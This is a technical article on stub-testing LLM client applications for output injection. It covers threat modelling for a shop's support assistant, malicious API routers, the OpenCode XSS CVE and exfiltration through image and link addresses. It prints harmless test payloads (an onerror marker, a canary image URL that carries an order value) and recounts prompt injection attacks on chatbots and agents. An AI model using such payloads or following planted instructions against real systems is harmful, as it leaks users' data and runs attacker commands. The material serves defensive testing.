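# Testing LLM Applications with a Stubbed Model API: Threat Modelling, Fuzzing and Penetration Tests for Output Injection

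## What a stubbed model API is and which bugs it looks for

Many programs send text to a large language model and then act on the reply, for example by showing it on a web page, posting it in a chat channel, running it as a database query or passing it to another program. Such a program is a client, and it reaches the model through an API, a web interface with a fixed format for requests and replies. A stubbed model API replaces the model with a stub, a small program that accepts the client's requests in the same format and returns whatever reply the tester chose. Developers and security testers use it to find and fix bugs in how the client handles hostile, broken or strange replies before release.

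Most of the bugs are old ones. Web developers have known for decades that text typed by a stranger must not run as code. A model's reply deserves the same suspicion, since strangers can often influence it. But developers easily forget this because the reply comes from a service they chose and pay for, and it nearly always looks harmless.

### One request and one reply

This section uses OpenAI's chat completion API as its example. Suppose a customer asks the support assistant on a shop's website where order 1182 is. The shop's client sends a request containing a model name, a list of tools the model may request, and a list of messages. OpenAI's *Create chat completion* describes the messages as the conversation so far. They include the shop's instructions and the customer's question. If the client has looked up other text, such as a product page or an old e-mail, that text usually goes into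 the same list.

The reply is a block of JSON, a text format for structured data. Shortened, and with invented values, it might look like this:

```json
{
  "id": "chatcmpl-example",
  "choices": [{
    "message": {
      "content": "I am checking **order 1182** now.",
      "tool_calls": [{
        "id": "call_1",
        "type": "function",
        "function": {
          "name": "find_order",
          "arguments": "{\"order_id\": \"1182\"}"
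        }
      }]
    },
    "finish_reason": "tool_calls"
  }],
  "usage": {"prompt_tokens": 64, "completion_tokens": 21, "total_tokens": 85}
}
```

The `content` field holds the text in Markdown, a simple markup language in which double asterisks mean bold. The shop's client converts the text to HTML and inserts it in the page.

Each entry under `tool_calls` contains a function's name and arguments. The client, not the model, looks up `find_order` among its own functions, parses the arguments and runs the function. The arguments arrive as a string that should itself contain JSON. OpenAI's *Chat* reference warns that the string may be invalid JSON or include parameters the developer never defined, and tells developers to validate the arguments before calling the function.

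The remaining fields are metadata. `finish_reason` records why the model stopped: `stop` for a natural end, `length` when it reached the token limit, `content_filter` when a filter removed something, and `tool_calls` when it produced a function call. Clients branch on this value, and one that ignores it may parse a truncated reply as if it were complete. `usage` counts tokens (the word fragments in which providers measure text) and typically ends up in a bill or a log. The model produces the text, the function name and the arguments, while the provider's server fills in fields such as `id` and `usage`. An attacker who can influence only the model can therefore affect some fields much more easily than others, although a stub can set them all.

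With streaming on, the same reply arrives in small pieces and the client joins them, often displaying incomplete sentences as it goes. OpenAI now recommends its newer Responses interface for new projects. The field names differ, but the client still has to handle the text and function calls it receives.

### Output injection and prompt injection

Output injection is a bug in which the component that receives text or data from the model interprets it as code, markup or commands. The sink is the place where the reply takes effect, such as a browser's HTML renderer, a terminal, a database or a command shell. If the shop's Markdown converter lets raw HTML through, a script element in a reply would run in the customer's browser, inside their logged-in session. This bug is known as cross-site scripting (XSS). If the client escapes the HTML characters first, the browser displays the script element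 as text.

Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* describes prompt injection as input that alters the model's behaviour in ways the developer did not intend. It is indirect when the attacker's text arrives in a document, web page or tool result that the client passed to the model. Prompt injection corrupts the model's output, while output injection is the client's failure to handle that output properly, whether or not prompt injection corrupted it.

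Either can happen without the other. *PROMPTFUZZ* (Yu, Shao and colleagues, 2024) gives the example of a site that asks a model to answer 1 if a comment is an advertisement and 0 if it is not. An advertiser writes a comment that tells the model to answer 0. The site reads the 0 correctly and publishes the advertisement, and escaping the output would not have helped. Conversely, someone may ask a coding assistant how script elements work and get back a correct example, which the page then runs. Nobody attacked anything, but the client has a serious vulnerability. The worst cases combine the two, and researchers have found such combinations in shipped products.

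The usual reference for the client's half is *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, an entry in the top ten risks for applications built on language models published by the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit. The entry defines the risk as insufficient validation, sanitization and handling of a model's output before it passes to other components. OWASP compares passing on unchecked output to giving users indirect access to additional functions, because prompts can control the output.

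| Sink | What the client does | What can follow |
|---|---|---|
| Command shell, or functions such as `exec` and `eval` | Enters the reply directly | Remote code execution: an attacker's commands run on the machine |
| Browser | Returns JavaScript or Markdown that the browser interprets | XSS |
| Database | Runs SQL from the model without keeping values apart from the query | SQL injection: the attacker rewrites the query |
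| File system | Builds a file path from the reply without cleaning it | Path traversal: access to files outside the intended folder |
| E-mail template | Inserts the reply without escaping it | Phishing |

OWASP distinguishes this risk from overreliance, where people believe wrong output. If the shop's assistant gives the wrong delivery date, the client has still handled the text correctly, so a stub will not find the error.

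The entry has had several numbers on OWASP's list. It began as *LLM02*, Insecure Output Handling, and is tenth in the edition that OWASP (2026) published in August. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a security vendor's summary, calls this the largest drop on the list. The entry's scope has still grown, and now explicitly covers terminals that act on escape codes and programs that automatically fetch resources named in a reply. The lower rank is weak evidence that the bug has become rare, because three quarters of the ranking comes from a vote among practitioners and only one quarter from 7,714 recorded incidents. Invicti attributes the drop to other risks being more urgent.

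### Where the method comes from

Embrace The Red's *Don't blindly trust LLM responses. Threats to chatbots*, a 2023 post by the security researcher Johann Rehberger, contains the original proposal. While building a command-line assistant and a Discord chatbot, Rehberger concluded that model output is untrusted data. The risks include familiar ones, such as XSS and SQL injection, and several specific to chat: a reply that tags everyone in a channel, one that starts with an exclamation mark and triggers a bot command, or a link with private data in its address that the chat platform fetches automatically.

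His remedies included threat modelling, manual penetration testing (an authorised tester attacks the system by hand), human review of risky actions and minimal permissions. He also suggested building a stub for calls to OpenAI's ChatCompletion API, then fuzzing the client to "bombard it with random responses to see how it behaves". He said only that this "might help catch some output injection issues". The suggestion is two sentences long and includes no test results. OWASP lists the post among the references for its output-handling entry.

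In January 2024 Wayne Roseberry, who writes about software testing, reached a similar idea from a different starting point. His *Security testing a chatbot* considers a demonstration by the data company Snowflake, in which a model turns a user's question into SQL and the application runs it on business data. He named three things at risk: computing time, which the owner pays for; data that the user should not see; and the integrity of the data itself. A tester could try to jailbreak the model, meaning to persuade it to ignore its instructions and write the attacker's query. Roseberry called that an arms race in cleverness and thought that even a robust prompt would eventually fail. He proposed instead to "assume jailbreak" by replacing the model with a mock that returns the SQL an attacker would want, then seeing how much damage follows.

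The argument is hard to fault as far as it goes. Roseberry observed that a web page with drop-down menus that assembled SQL would face the same attack, so the threat lies in what the application does with the model's reply. If the database account can read only the tables the user may see, it no longer matters much how a query for other tables was produced. Testing then becomes largely an audit of permissions and settings, which a team can finish, whereas attempts to outsmart a model have no clear end. He still wanted testers to try actual attacks on each asset and to make some attempts to outsmart the bot.

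But he called the idea "pure invention, pure thought experiment". He had no specification or code in front of him, had not tried it on Snowflake's demonstration, and did not know how well it would work. So neither of the founding posts shows the method catching a bug. The premise has since become standard advice. Infosecurity Magazine reports that OWASP now tells developers to assume that a model's instruction boundary will eventually fail, and to restrict what the model's outputs can reach.

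Rehberger's version and Roseberry's also complement each other. Random replies can reveal faults nobody had thought of, but they may never include a working SQL statement. A tester who writes the SQL on purpose will test the obvious danger at once but miss the unusual ones.

### Why take the model out

Software developers routinely test with a stand-in for an outside service, often called a mock. *Are Coding Agents Generating Over-Mocked Tests?* (2026) explains that this makes tests fast, repeatable and deterministic. These benefits matter more than usual with language models, which the *Testing* page for AI SDK, a toolkit for building LLM applications, describes as non-deterministic and "slow and expensive" to call. A stub needs no live model, network access or API key, as Genkit's *Testing your AI logic* says of its own mock models. A team can therefore run thousands of replies through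 the client after every code change.

Repeatability matters most when a test fails. *Towards Risk-free AI Agent Deployment* (2026) points out that with a live model, the same test may pass once and fail the next time although nothing in the system has changed, and developers may be unable to tell a real defect from random variation in sampling. OpenAI's `seed` setting was a partial remedy, but OpenAI promised only a "best effort" and has since deprecated the setting. Providers also change models without notice, which *Testing the Untestable?* (2025) lists among the difficulties of testing this kind of software. With a stub, the reply that broke the client is saved in a file, so the developer can replay it until the fix works and keep it as a permanent test.

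A stub also helps with security testing because it sends the tester's chosen script element or shell command on the first attempt, while a live model may decline to write it. If the model declines, the test passes without showing what the client would have done with that text. A later version of the model might still produce it, or a more patient attacker might elicit it.

Tests with a stubbed API reveal nothing about the model. According to Pydantic's *Unit testing* guide, such tests check the developer's own code, and the quality of the answers is left to separate evaluations. Finding out whether a real model would ever send the hostile reply also requires tests against the real model. There is also little published evidence for the practical benefits of stubbing. *Automated structural testing of LLM-based agents* (2026) reports that mocks, combined with execution traces and automatic assertions,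 made tests easier to automate and the root causes of failures quicker to find, but its evaluation is qualitative.

### Fuzzing the client or fuzzing the prompt

Fuzzing means running a program on many generated inputs and watching for failures. Yu and colleagues describe black-box fuzzing, which requires no knowledge of the program's internals, as a loop. The fuzzer starts with a pool of sample inputs, called seeds. It picks one, alters it (for instance, by flipping bits or splicing in dictionary entries), runs the target on the result and checks the response for bugs or unexpected behaviour. It returns interesting inputs to the pool for further rounds. When a tester uses a stub to fuzz a client, the client is the target and the model's reply is the input. The JSON reply above could serve as a seed. Variants might break off in the middle of the arguments, name a function that does not exist,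 or put markup where the order number belongs.

Prompt fuzzing uses the same loop to test the model. In PromptFuzz, Yu and colleagues' tool, the target is a live model and the inputs are prompts. An attack succeeds when the model reveals information the developer wanted kept secret or produces text the attacker dictated. Flipping bits would turn a prompt into nonsense, so the tool has a language model rephrase, lengthen, shorten and combine prompts while preserving their meaning. Within two hours, its prompts reached seventh place among more than 4,000 entrants in a prompt injection contest, and it still found successful attacks after the researchers had trained a model to resist them. Prompt fuzzing doesn't test the code that receives the reply, so it can miss a client that runs any script it is sent. Stubbed replies can catch that bug, but they don't test whether the model itself can be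 hijacked.

### The order of work

A full test of a client goes through five steps, each of which needs the one before.

1. Draw a threat model, which is a map of who can influence the reply and of every sink where the reply ends up. It determines which replies are worth sending.
2. Build the stub and point the client at it, leaving the rest of the client as close to the released version as possible.
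3. Write a generator that supplies the stub with replies: deliberate attacks for each sink on the map, and random or damaged replies for whatever the map missed. The payload, the part of a reply meant to trigger a sink, is always a harmless marker.
4. Write an oracle, the automatic check that decides whether a reply caused a failure. A crash is easy to notice, but a client that quietly fetches a link is not. Testers therefore plant canaries, unique markers such as a test-only web address, and search for them in places they should never reach.
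5. Test by hand against the real model. A person can find what the generator did not think to try, and can establish reachability: whether an attacker could cause the deployed system to receive the reply that broke the client under test.

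## Drawing the threat model: who can shape a response and where it goes

The threat model shows who can influence the reply, where the reply goes, and how much harm it could do there. Testers draw the threat model in five steps.

1. Draw the data flow. Start at the code that calls the model API. Trace the request back to every place its text came from, then trace the reply forward to every place any part of it ends up. Logs, saved records and later requests to the model all count.
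2. Mark the whole reply as untrusted from the moment it enters the client. Anything the client copies or derives from it stays untrusted too, so a summary saved in a database is as suspect a month later as on the day it arrived.
3. List every sink. Search the code for each use of the reply's text, function names, arguments and metadata, and work out which component interprets it.
4. Note the privileges at each sink: whose account or session the component uses, what it can read, change or contact, and whether a person approves the action first.
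5. Pair each source of hostile replies with each sink it can reach, and rank the pairs by how easily an attacker could use them and how much harm would follow.

### A support assistant with four sinks

Suppose the shop whose customer asked about order 1182 has extended its support assistant. The client runs on the shop's server and now uses the model's replies in four places:

- The web chat page converts the reply from Markdown to HTML and shows it to a logged-in customer.
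- The database lookup tool, `find_order`, takes an order number from the tool call and queries the order database. Its database account can read every customer's orders.
- The staff terminal tool prints the model's summaries of open tickets, one per line, when a support worker runs it on their own computer.
- The chat notifier posts a short summary in the staff's chat channel when a customer needs a person. It posts as a bot that can tag the whole channel, and the chat platform fetches any link in a post to build a preview.

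The client builds its requests from the customer's message, product reviews, supplier e-mails, and other customers' tickets about the same product. It sends them to the model through a router, a service that forwards requests to one or more model providers. The shop runs the router itself.

```
REQUEST   customer's message, reviews,
          supplier e-mails, stored tickets --> client --> router --> model server

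REPLY     model server --> router --> client --> web chat page

--> find_order --> order database

--> ticket summary --> staff terminal tool

--> chat notifier --> staff channel
```

The diagram omits two loops. The result of each order lookup goes back to the model in the next request. The model also writes ticket summaries, which become part of the stored tickets it reads for later customers. A hostile reply can therefore cause trouble long after its conversation ends.

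### Why the model counts as an attacker

The security consultancy NCC Group extends step 2 with a method called Models-As-Threat-Actors, which adds the model itself to the map as a possible attacker. In *Analyzing AI Application Threat Models*, its consultant nccdavid (2024) argues that outsiders can usually influence a model, so designers should ask what a hostile person could do from the model's position and deny the model anything they would deny that person. nccdavid has little confidence in controls inside the model, or in a second model that monitors the first, and recommends ordinary access controls that match the end user's permissions.

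On the shop's map, this reveals a fault before any testing. The account behind `find_order` can read every customer's orders, although customers are allowed to see only their own.

The customer is the most obvious source of hostile text. A customer who gets the model to write a script element for the chat page will mostly harm their own browser session, but their text also reaches staff screens and database lookups, where it can harm others.

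An attacker can plant instructions in third-party text without ever contacting the assistant. *The Dark Side of LLMs* (2025) tested eighteen models in agents, programs in which a model chooses actions and software carries them out. In one attack, the users behaved normally, and the attacker only had to alter a document in the agent's knowledge base and wait for the agent to process it. The malicious instruction was all in a single passage to make retrieval more likely, so the experiment doesn't measure how often an agent would come across such a document by itself. Attackers could reach the shop the same way, through product reviews and supplier e-mails.

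A third way to influence a response is through another user's stored data. nccdavid uses the term "persistent world" for a system in which one person's data can affect the model's replies to someone else. In nccdavid's example, a model summarises forum threads, and an attacker posts a comment that alters the summary for everyone who requests it. A subtler attack is possible if the client builds its request by joining fields with line breaks. An attacker can then put a line break in a field they control, such as a username, and add a false value for a field they do not control. Models interpret text loosely, so nccdavid warns that this might work even on fields that the client has cleaned properly. In the shop, a customer might get a false statement into a ticket summary by adding a second line to their display name that reads "refund approved".

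Format corruption is an attack on whatever parses the output. nccdavid gives the example of an application that handles CSV files, where an attacker who gets the model to add a comma may shift every later value in the row into the wrong column. The staff terminal tool has the same weakness if it treats each line as a separate ticket, because a line break in a summary could make a fake ticket appear. These attacks need no script or command, so a tester who looks only for classic injection payloads would miss them.

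An oracle attack extracts information from a model whose output the attacker never sees. (The name is unrelated to a test oracle.) nccdavid imagines a site that has a model judge whether a joke is funny and returns a server error if the model answers anything except "funny" or "unfunny". The attacker submits a "joke" that tells the model to answer "funny" if its hidden instructions begin with a letter from A to M, and "unfunny" otherwise. Halving the range each time takes at most five questions per letter, plus some repeats because models make mistakes. The client contributes to this leak by turning a hidden answer into a visible difference. The shop's customers never see the staff channel, but if the page announces that a member of staff is on the way, they get one yes-or-no answer per message.

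### When the reply changes on the way

All of these attackers have to get the model to produce the output they want. Whoever controls the model server can return anything they like without involving the model. This is a practical concern when users can connect a client to a server of their choice, as the malicious-server flaw in the chat interface Open WebUI showed. Whoever controls a router can do the same, a threat that researchers studied closely in 2026.

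Developers use routers to reach many models with one key, to save money, or to get access in regions where a provider does not operate. Adding one usually means changing only the web address of the API. The connection is still encrypted with TLS, the standard protection for web traffic. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (Xie, Wu and colleagues, 2026) explains that the router ends the client's TLS session and opens a separate one to the provider. The client may appear to have a secure line to the provider, but the router holds the whole exchange as readable text. The client can verify that it is talking to the router it chose, but not that the router passed on the provider's exact reply.

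*Rewriting the Response Path* (Luo, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) defines a reply as r = (x, c), where x is the text a person reads and c is the part the client executes, such as a tool call. The client should run c only if the model S produced it, a condition the paper writes as auth_S(c) = 1. Current clients never check this condition, so a router can substitute any c′ in the right format and the client will run it. Stub testing depends on the same gap, because the client accepts a stub's replies without proof of their origin.

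The main predecessor of this work is a survey of the router market. Liu, Shou and colleagues (2026), in *Your Agent Is Mine*, distinguished four attacks:

- The router rewrites a tool call so that it runs the attacker's command.
- It swaps the name of a software package in an install command for that of a malicious package.
- It alters replies only under chosen conditions, so that a brief test finds nothing.
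- It changes nothing, but copies passwords and keys from the traffic.

The researchers bought access to 28 routers and collected 400 free ones. Nine of the 428, including one paid router, inserted malicious code into tool calls. Seventeen used Amazon cloud credentials that the researchers had planted as canaries, and one emptied a planted cryptocurrency wallet. Crosley (2026), in *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet*, a blog post based on the full paper, adds that one router did nothing malicious during its first 50 requests. Another attacked only sessions that ran commands without asking for approval and worked on Rust or Go projects.

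Nine in 428 is about 2%, which may be an undercount because a malicious router would have looked honest if its trigger never fired. The sample came mostly from Chinese-language marketplaces and communities, so it is weak evidence about large commercial gateways. The client's owner also may not know every router on the path. Crosley recounts the paper's example of a developer who buys from a reseller, who uses an aggregator, which goes through another router to reach the model's host. The developer configures only the first of these, but any of them can change the reply.

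Attackers can also compromise a router that a company runs itself. Obsidian Security's *Breaking LiteLLM* describes three vulnerabilities in LiteLLM, a widely used open-source router, that together let an ordinary user become an administrator and run code on the server. The firm also demonstrated that a router compromised in this way can insert tool calls into the replies it forwards to agents such as Claude Code, Anthropic's coding assistant. The shop's threat model therefore needs to include the router even if the shop runs it itself.

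### Whether clients act on altered replies

Liu and colleagues built a malicious router and found that four agent programs accepted nearly all of its altered tool calls as valid. Crosley points out that this measured only delivery, and that a permission prompt or a sandbox might still have stopped the commands from running.

In *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?*, Fu, Li and colleagues (2026) used a set-up very like a stub to measure whether coding agents executed malicious tool calls. They recorded the agents' exchanges with a model, then replayed the replies with one malicious call inserted at a random turn. They wrote 400 such calls and tried each on three programming tasks. The crudest alterations replaced the whole reply, and the subtlest regenerated it so that the explanation fitted the malicious command. Claude Code, Codex, Cursor and OpenCode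 blocked none of the calls.

That result rests on only three tasks, with one run per combination, and it doesn't cover Claude Code's default mode, in which a person approves actions. Two of the failures still matter for threat modelling. Claude Code's planning mode is read-only, but the restriction existed only as an instruction to the model, so it didn't block a call that the router added after the model had answered. Other modes ask a model to review risky actions, and those review requests went through the same router. A check offers little protection if it relies on the component it is checking, so testers should also draw each safeguard's path on the map.

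Luo and colleagues report high but less uniform figures. On Agent Security Bench, a set of tasks for agents in ten roles, changing one field redirected agents on 89.1% of tasks, averaged over five models, compared with 42.6% for direct prompt injection. They acknowledge that the two attacks are not directly comparable, because prompt injection has to overcome the model's safety training, while a router alters the model's response afterwards. In another experiment, the router inserted security weaknesses into repairs to Django, a web framework. A hidden security check failed in 69.0% of 60 runs, against 10.5% without tampering, yet about half of the altered repairs still passed the public tests that a developer would look at. Of 25 popular agents and chat programs for which a custom API address made sense, 23 accepted one and so could be pointed at a router, though this figure doesn't show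 how many users set such an address.

Client-side defences can stop some attacks. An allowlist lets clients contact only approved web domains and install only approved packages. Crosley reports that Liu and colleagues' allowlist blocked every plain attack in a synthetic test, but failed every time against an attacker who knew about it and put the malicious file on an approved domain. In tests by Fu and colleagues, an allowlist stopped only 31% to 44% of the malicious calls. Much of the difference is probably because their collection included harmful file edits and faulty code, which often contain no domain or package to check. Reviewer models that the client reached directly, without the router, stopped between 39% and 64%.

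A real fix must let the client verify where a reply came from. Luo and colleagues propose that the provider sign the tool calls and the finish reason, so that a small program beside the client can reject altered ones. In their tests, it rejected them all. The signature does not cover the reply's text, so a router could still put hostile markup into the shop's chat page unless a separate, optional layer of encryption protects the text. Xie and colleagues instead move the part of the router that handles messages into a hardware enclave, which is protected memory that the router's operator can neither read nor change. Neither design would stop a hostile reply that the model itself wrote, so the client has to treat even an authenticated reply as untrusted.

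### Errors without an attacker

Some harmful responses occur without an attacker. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) describes cases where Claude exploited a basic software flaw to run commands on a server, or submitted a sensitive form on a real website when it should not have. Anthropic found minimal real-world impact, but a client that carries out tool calls needs limits that apply even when there is no attacker.

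Mistakes in ordinary text matter as well. A model may quote a customer's HTML in a ticket summary, invent a function name, or give an order number as a sentence. nccdavid discusses a more serious case, a factory where a model decides when conditions are dangerous enough to stop production. Few outsiders could influence such a model, but it might still fail to stop the machines. nccdavid recommends a fixed check that can halt production under conditions known to be dangerous, whatever the model concludes. A sink on the map therefore needs a test if a plain error there would do enough harm, even if no attacker can reach it.

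### What AI Village's threat model leaves out

A threat model can also miss bugs because of what it assumes. In *Threat Modeling LLM Applications*, GTKlondike drew a threat model for the AI security community AI Village, just after OWASP began work on its top ten for language model applications. The diagram has four elements: outside sources of prompts, the model, server-side functions, and private data. Trust boundaries, which mark where data passes between parts that should not automatically trust each other, separate the model from each of the other three. GTKlondike checks each boundary against STRIDE, a standard list of threats: spoofing, tampering, repudiation, information disclosure, denial of service and elevation of privilege. The boundary between the model and the outside world applies in both directions, because outsiders can influence the model's output as well as its input.

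Like nccdavid, GTKlondike concludes that developers should treat all model output as untrusted. But the AI Village threat model assumes that the surrounding application already follows OWASP's advice for ordinary web applications, and it puts traditional application flaws out of scope. That is sensible for its purpose, which was to isolate what is new about language models. However, most output injection bugs are traditional flaws, so the assumption excludes what a stub test is meant to find. On the shop's map, it would mean treating the chat page and the order query as safe without checking them. The effect is visible in GTKlondike's own lists, where XSS is not among the four vulnerabilities for the boundary between the model and the user, even though the text mentions a reply that carries XSS back to a user.

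nccdavid also concentrates on attacks that are new with machine learning, but considers how they combine with traditional vulnerabilities and does not take the rest of the application to be sound. That makes the NCC method the better starting point here, though AI Village's boundaries are a useful aid for drawing the diagram.

The AI Village model has other exclusions that would cause the shop to miss some tests. It leaves out denial of service, so it doesn't cover a reply that never ends. It shows the LLM as a single box, so there is nowhere to put a router. GTKlondike also excludes made-up facts as a known limitation to plan around. That is fair for LLMs, but the client still has to handle a made-up function name. Testers can avoid most of these gaps by writing each assumption on the map as a claim to test, such as "The chat page escapes HTML."

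### Ranking the shop's pairs

The shop has six sources of hostile replies: the customer, third-party text, other customers' stored tickets, the model server, the router, and the model's own errors. Pairing each source with each of the four sinks gives 24 pairs. A pair's rank depends on what an attacker must already control to use the source and what the sink would let them do that they could not do themselves. The table groups pairs that are similar in both respects.

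| Source | Sink | Privileges at the sink | Test priority |
|---|---|---|---|
| Customer's message | `find_order` | Database account that can read every customer's orders; nobody approves the query | High: any customer can try it, and it may expose other people's data |
| Customer's message, third-party text, stored tickets | Staff terminal tool | The support worker's account on their own computer | High: an outsider's words reach an employee's machine |
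| Third-party text, stored tickets | Web chat page | The session of a logged-in customer | High: the victim only has to ask an ordinary question |
| Customer's message, third-party text, stored tickets | Chat notifier | Bot that can tag the whole channel; the platform fetches links | Medium: easy to try, but the bot can do little except post |
| Third-party text, stored tickets | `find_order` | Same database account | Medium: the attacker also needs a way to get the result out |
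| Router, model server | All four sinks, and any code that reads metadata | All of the above | Medium: the attacker must first control a server, but can then set every field |
| Model's own error | All four sinks | All of the above | Medium: needs no attacker, but rarely produces the most damaging reply |
| Customer's message | Web chat page | The customer's own session | Low: the customer mostly attacks themselves |

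These priorities are judgements, and another tester might reasonably rank the chat notifier higher, because a link that the platform fetches automatically could carry private data out of the company.

The client handles a hostile reply the same way whatever its source, so one set of replies for the chat page tests both a high-priority row and the low-priority row. The source still determines which fields a tester should fill with hostile values. The router and model server add the metadata, so either could send a negative token count, a repeated `id`, or a `finish_reason` that no provider has defined. Testers who consider only prompt injection would not test those fields.

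Some rows need a design change before testing. For the first row, the shop should give `find_order` an account that can read only the current customer's orders.

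## Output that is displayed: web pages, chat apps and terminals

Three of the shop's four sinks only display text: the web chat page, the chat notifier and the staff terminal tool. But browsers, chat platforms and terminals treat some characters as instructions. A less-than sign can open an HTML element, a web address can trigger a download, and an invisible control character can move the cursor. If a client passes these characters on unchanged, anyone who shaped the reply can send instructions to the browser, chat platform or terminal.

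### How a reply becomes script

The shop's Markdown renderer converts each reply to HTML, and the client inserts the result into the DOM, the tree of elements that the browser displays. Markdown permits raw HTML, so many renderers copy any HTML in the reply straight into the page. The browser cannot distinguish the reply's elements from the shop's own.

The obvious test payload is a script element, but it can give a false pass. Pages usually add converted Markdown through a property called `innerHTML`, and browsers do not run script elements inserted that way. An image with an error handler is a better marker:

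```html
<img src="/missing-a17.png" onerror="document.title='canary-a17'">
```

The image file does not exist, so it fails to load and the browser runs the handler. If the browser tab's title changes to `canary-a17`, the script in the reply has run. If the page shows the code as text, the client escaped it.

Testers should also try a Markdown link whose address starts with `javascript:`, which a browser may run as code when someone clicks it. The link contains no HTML tags, so it can get past a client that escapes HTML characters before converting the Markdown.

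### OpenCode's renderer and CVE-2026-22813

OpenCode, an open-source coding agent, had this bug in its web interface. *CVE-2026-22813 Detail* (2026), an entry in the US government's National Vulnerability Database (NVD), records that the Markdown renderer inserted arbitrary HTML from replies into the page. OpenCode did not use a sanitizer, such as the DOMPurify library, to remove dangerous HTML. It also did not set a content security policy (CSP), a list of the scripts, images and other resources that the browser lets a page use. The flaw has a severity score of 9.4 out of 10.

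The score is so high because script on this page could run commands on the user's computer. GitHub's *GHSA-C83V-7274-4VGP* (2026), the project's security advisory, explains how:

1. When a developer starts OpenCode in a terminal, it automatically starts a web server on port 4096 of the same computer. That server provides both the web interface and OpenCode's own API.
2. The API has endpoints under `/pty/` that can start any program on the computer.
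3. Browsers let script on a page send any request to the server that the page came from. Script in the web interface could therefore call `/pty/`.

The server also required no password. GitLab's *CVE-2026-22812* (2026) describes this as a separate flaw, made worse by settings that let other websites call the API. In versions with that flaw, a malicious website could attack the server without using the Markdown bug.

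The attacker in GitHub's advisory supplied the reply without using a model or prompt injection. OpenCode's web interface accepted a `url` parameter that made it load chat sessions from another server. An attacker could host a session containing a hostile message, then trick a developer into opening a link to the OpenCode page on the developer's own computer, with the `url` parameter set to the attacker's server. Because the page itself was genuine and local, script in the message ran with that page's access.

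The proof of concept works much like a stub test. It puts a proxy in front of a real OpenCode server and replaces only the session data, because the interface has to load many other resources before it displays a chat. The message contains a hidden image whose error handler calls the API to create an empty file in a temporary folder. The file is harmless, but its presence shows that displayed text caused a command to run.

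Testing with a stubbed model API could have exposed the renderer bug, but not the `url` parameter, which bypassed the API. To find that parameter, a tester would have had to ask during threat modelling where else the page could load messages from.

OpenCode's developers fixed the problem in two stages. On 9 January 2026 they made the web interface ignore the `url` parameter. They could do this for every user at once, because the local page loaded its static files from a remote server that they controlled. Version 1.1.10 then disabled the web interface and its API. GitHub still urged users to upgrade, since any future XSS bug in the interface would affect older versions.

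Both measures block the attack but leave the renderer unrepaired, and the advisory mentions no added sanitizer. Anyone who turns the interface back on should test the renderer again. MITRE's *Malicious website can execute commands on the local system* (2026), the flaw's record in the public CVE catalogue, includes a 13 January assessment by the US cybersecurity agency CISA. CISA listed a proof of concept but no active attacks, and judged that attackers could automate the exploit and gain total control.

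### Keeping script out of the page

The simplest fix is to escape the whole reply, turning each `<` into `&lt;`. This works for pages that need only plain text. The shop wants to show bold text and lists, so it needs a sanitizer, which parses the HTML and keeps only approved elements and attributes.

The client should run the sanitizer after converting the Markdown, because conversion can create dangerous HTML, such as the `javascript:` link, that was not in the original text. If the response is streamed, the client should sanitize all the text received so far each time it updates the page, because an element split across two pieces may look harmless in each.

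A CSP is a second barrier in case the sanitizer misses something. A strict policy stops the browser from running scripts written directly into the page, including error handlers. Many sites weaken their policy to keep old code working, so testers should send the marker with the sanitizer off as well as on. A pass with the sanitizer on shows only that at least one of the two barriers works.

A CSP that only limited network requests to the page's own server would not have protected OpenCode, because the command endpoint was on that server. Keeping the endpoint away from the page that displays replies would have been safer. Script on the shop's chat page can likewise do whatever the logged-in customer can do, so the shop might require customers to re-enter their password before changing a delivery address or spending store credit.

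Neither measure removes every harmful element. DOMPurify's default settings keep ordinary images and links, which contain no script but can still leak data.

### How an image address carries data out

To display an image, the browser requests the file from the server named in the image's address. The request contains the full address, which the server usually logs. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains how an attacker can exploit this. Instructions hidden in a web page tell the model to add private information to the end of an image address on the attacker's server. When the browser loads the image, the information arrives in the attacker's log. The user doesn't have to click anything and may not notice.

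A test needs only a Markdown image with a made-up value in its address:

```markdown
![canary](https://canary.example/a17.png?order=TEST-1182)
```

The tester replaces the domain with a server they control. A request for `a17.png` in that server's log means the client loads images from outside addresses. It doesn't show that a model would put a real order number in the image address, which is a question of reachability.

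This was among the most common security bugs in early LLM products. Rehberger (2024), in *Trust No AI*, listed eleven affected products in which he had found and reported it:

- Microsoft's Bing Chat, Azure AI and GitHub Copilot Chat
- OpenAI's ChatGPT
- Anthropic's Claude
- Google's Bard, Vertex AI, NotebookLM, AI Studio and Colab
- Discord

The list comes from one researcher's reports, so it shows how widely the bug had spread but not what share of products had it.

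Rehberger reported the leak to both OpenAI and Microsoft in 2023, according to *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on his blog, Embrace The Red. Microsoft responded that May by blocking most images in Bing Chat with a CSP. OpenAI did not add its `url_safe` check until December, and Rehberger found ways around it. OpenAI had also left the check out of some apps.

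ChatGPT gained a long-term memory in 2024, and Rehberger found that a web page could use prompt injection to plant instructions there. Because the macOS app lacked the check, the planted instructions made it leak everything the user discussed with ChatGPT, even in later conversations. A team with a website, a phone app and a desktop app therefore has to test all three, even if they use the same model and API.

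Links can carry data too, although the user has to click them. In February 2024 Rehberger discovered an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that began with a phishing email. Instructions in the email made Copilot search the inbox for sensitive information and place it in a link, in invisible characters. Microsoft fixed the flaw that July. Amazon solved a similar problem in its Q for Business assistant by no longer rendering links.

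### ChatGPhish

*ChatGPhish*, published by the security company Permiso on 29 May 2026, describes a more recent case. The researchers added instructions to a project description on GitHub, opened the page in Firefox and asked ChatGPT to summarise it. ChatGPT summarised the page, then added a fake notice that someone had added a new device to the user's account, with a live link of the attacker's choice. The researchers got the same result with an ordinary web page on their own server. They stress that this is not a flaw in Firefox, which only passes the page's text to ChatGPT.

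Two variants used images. In one, the reply displayed a QR code. Scanning it with a phone would bypass the computer's protections, such as link previews and lists of blocked sites. In the other, the image loaded through a link-shortening service. The request revealed the user's IP address, browser type, sometimes the referring page, and when ChatGPT produced the answer. An attacker could use this to confirm that a particular target had read a particular page.

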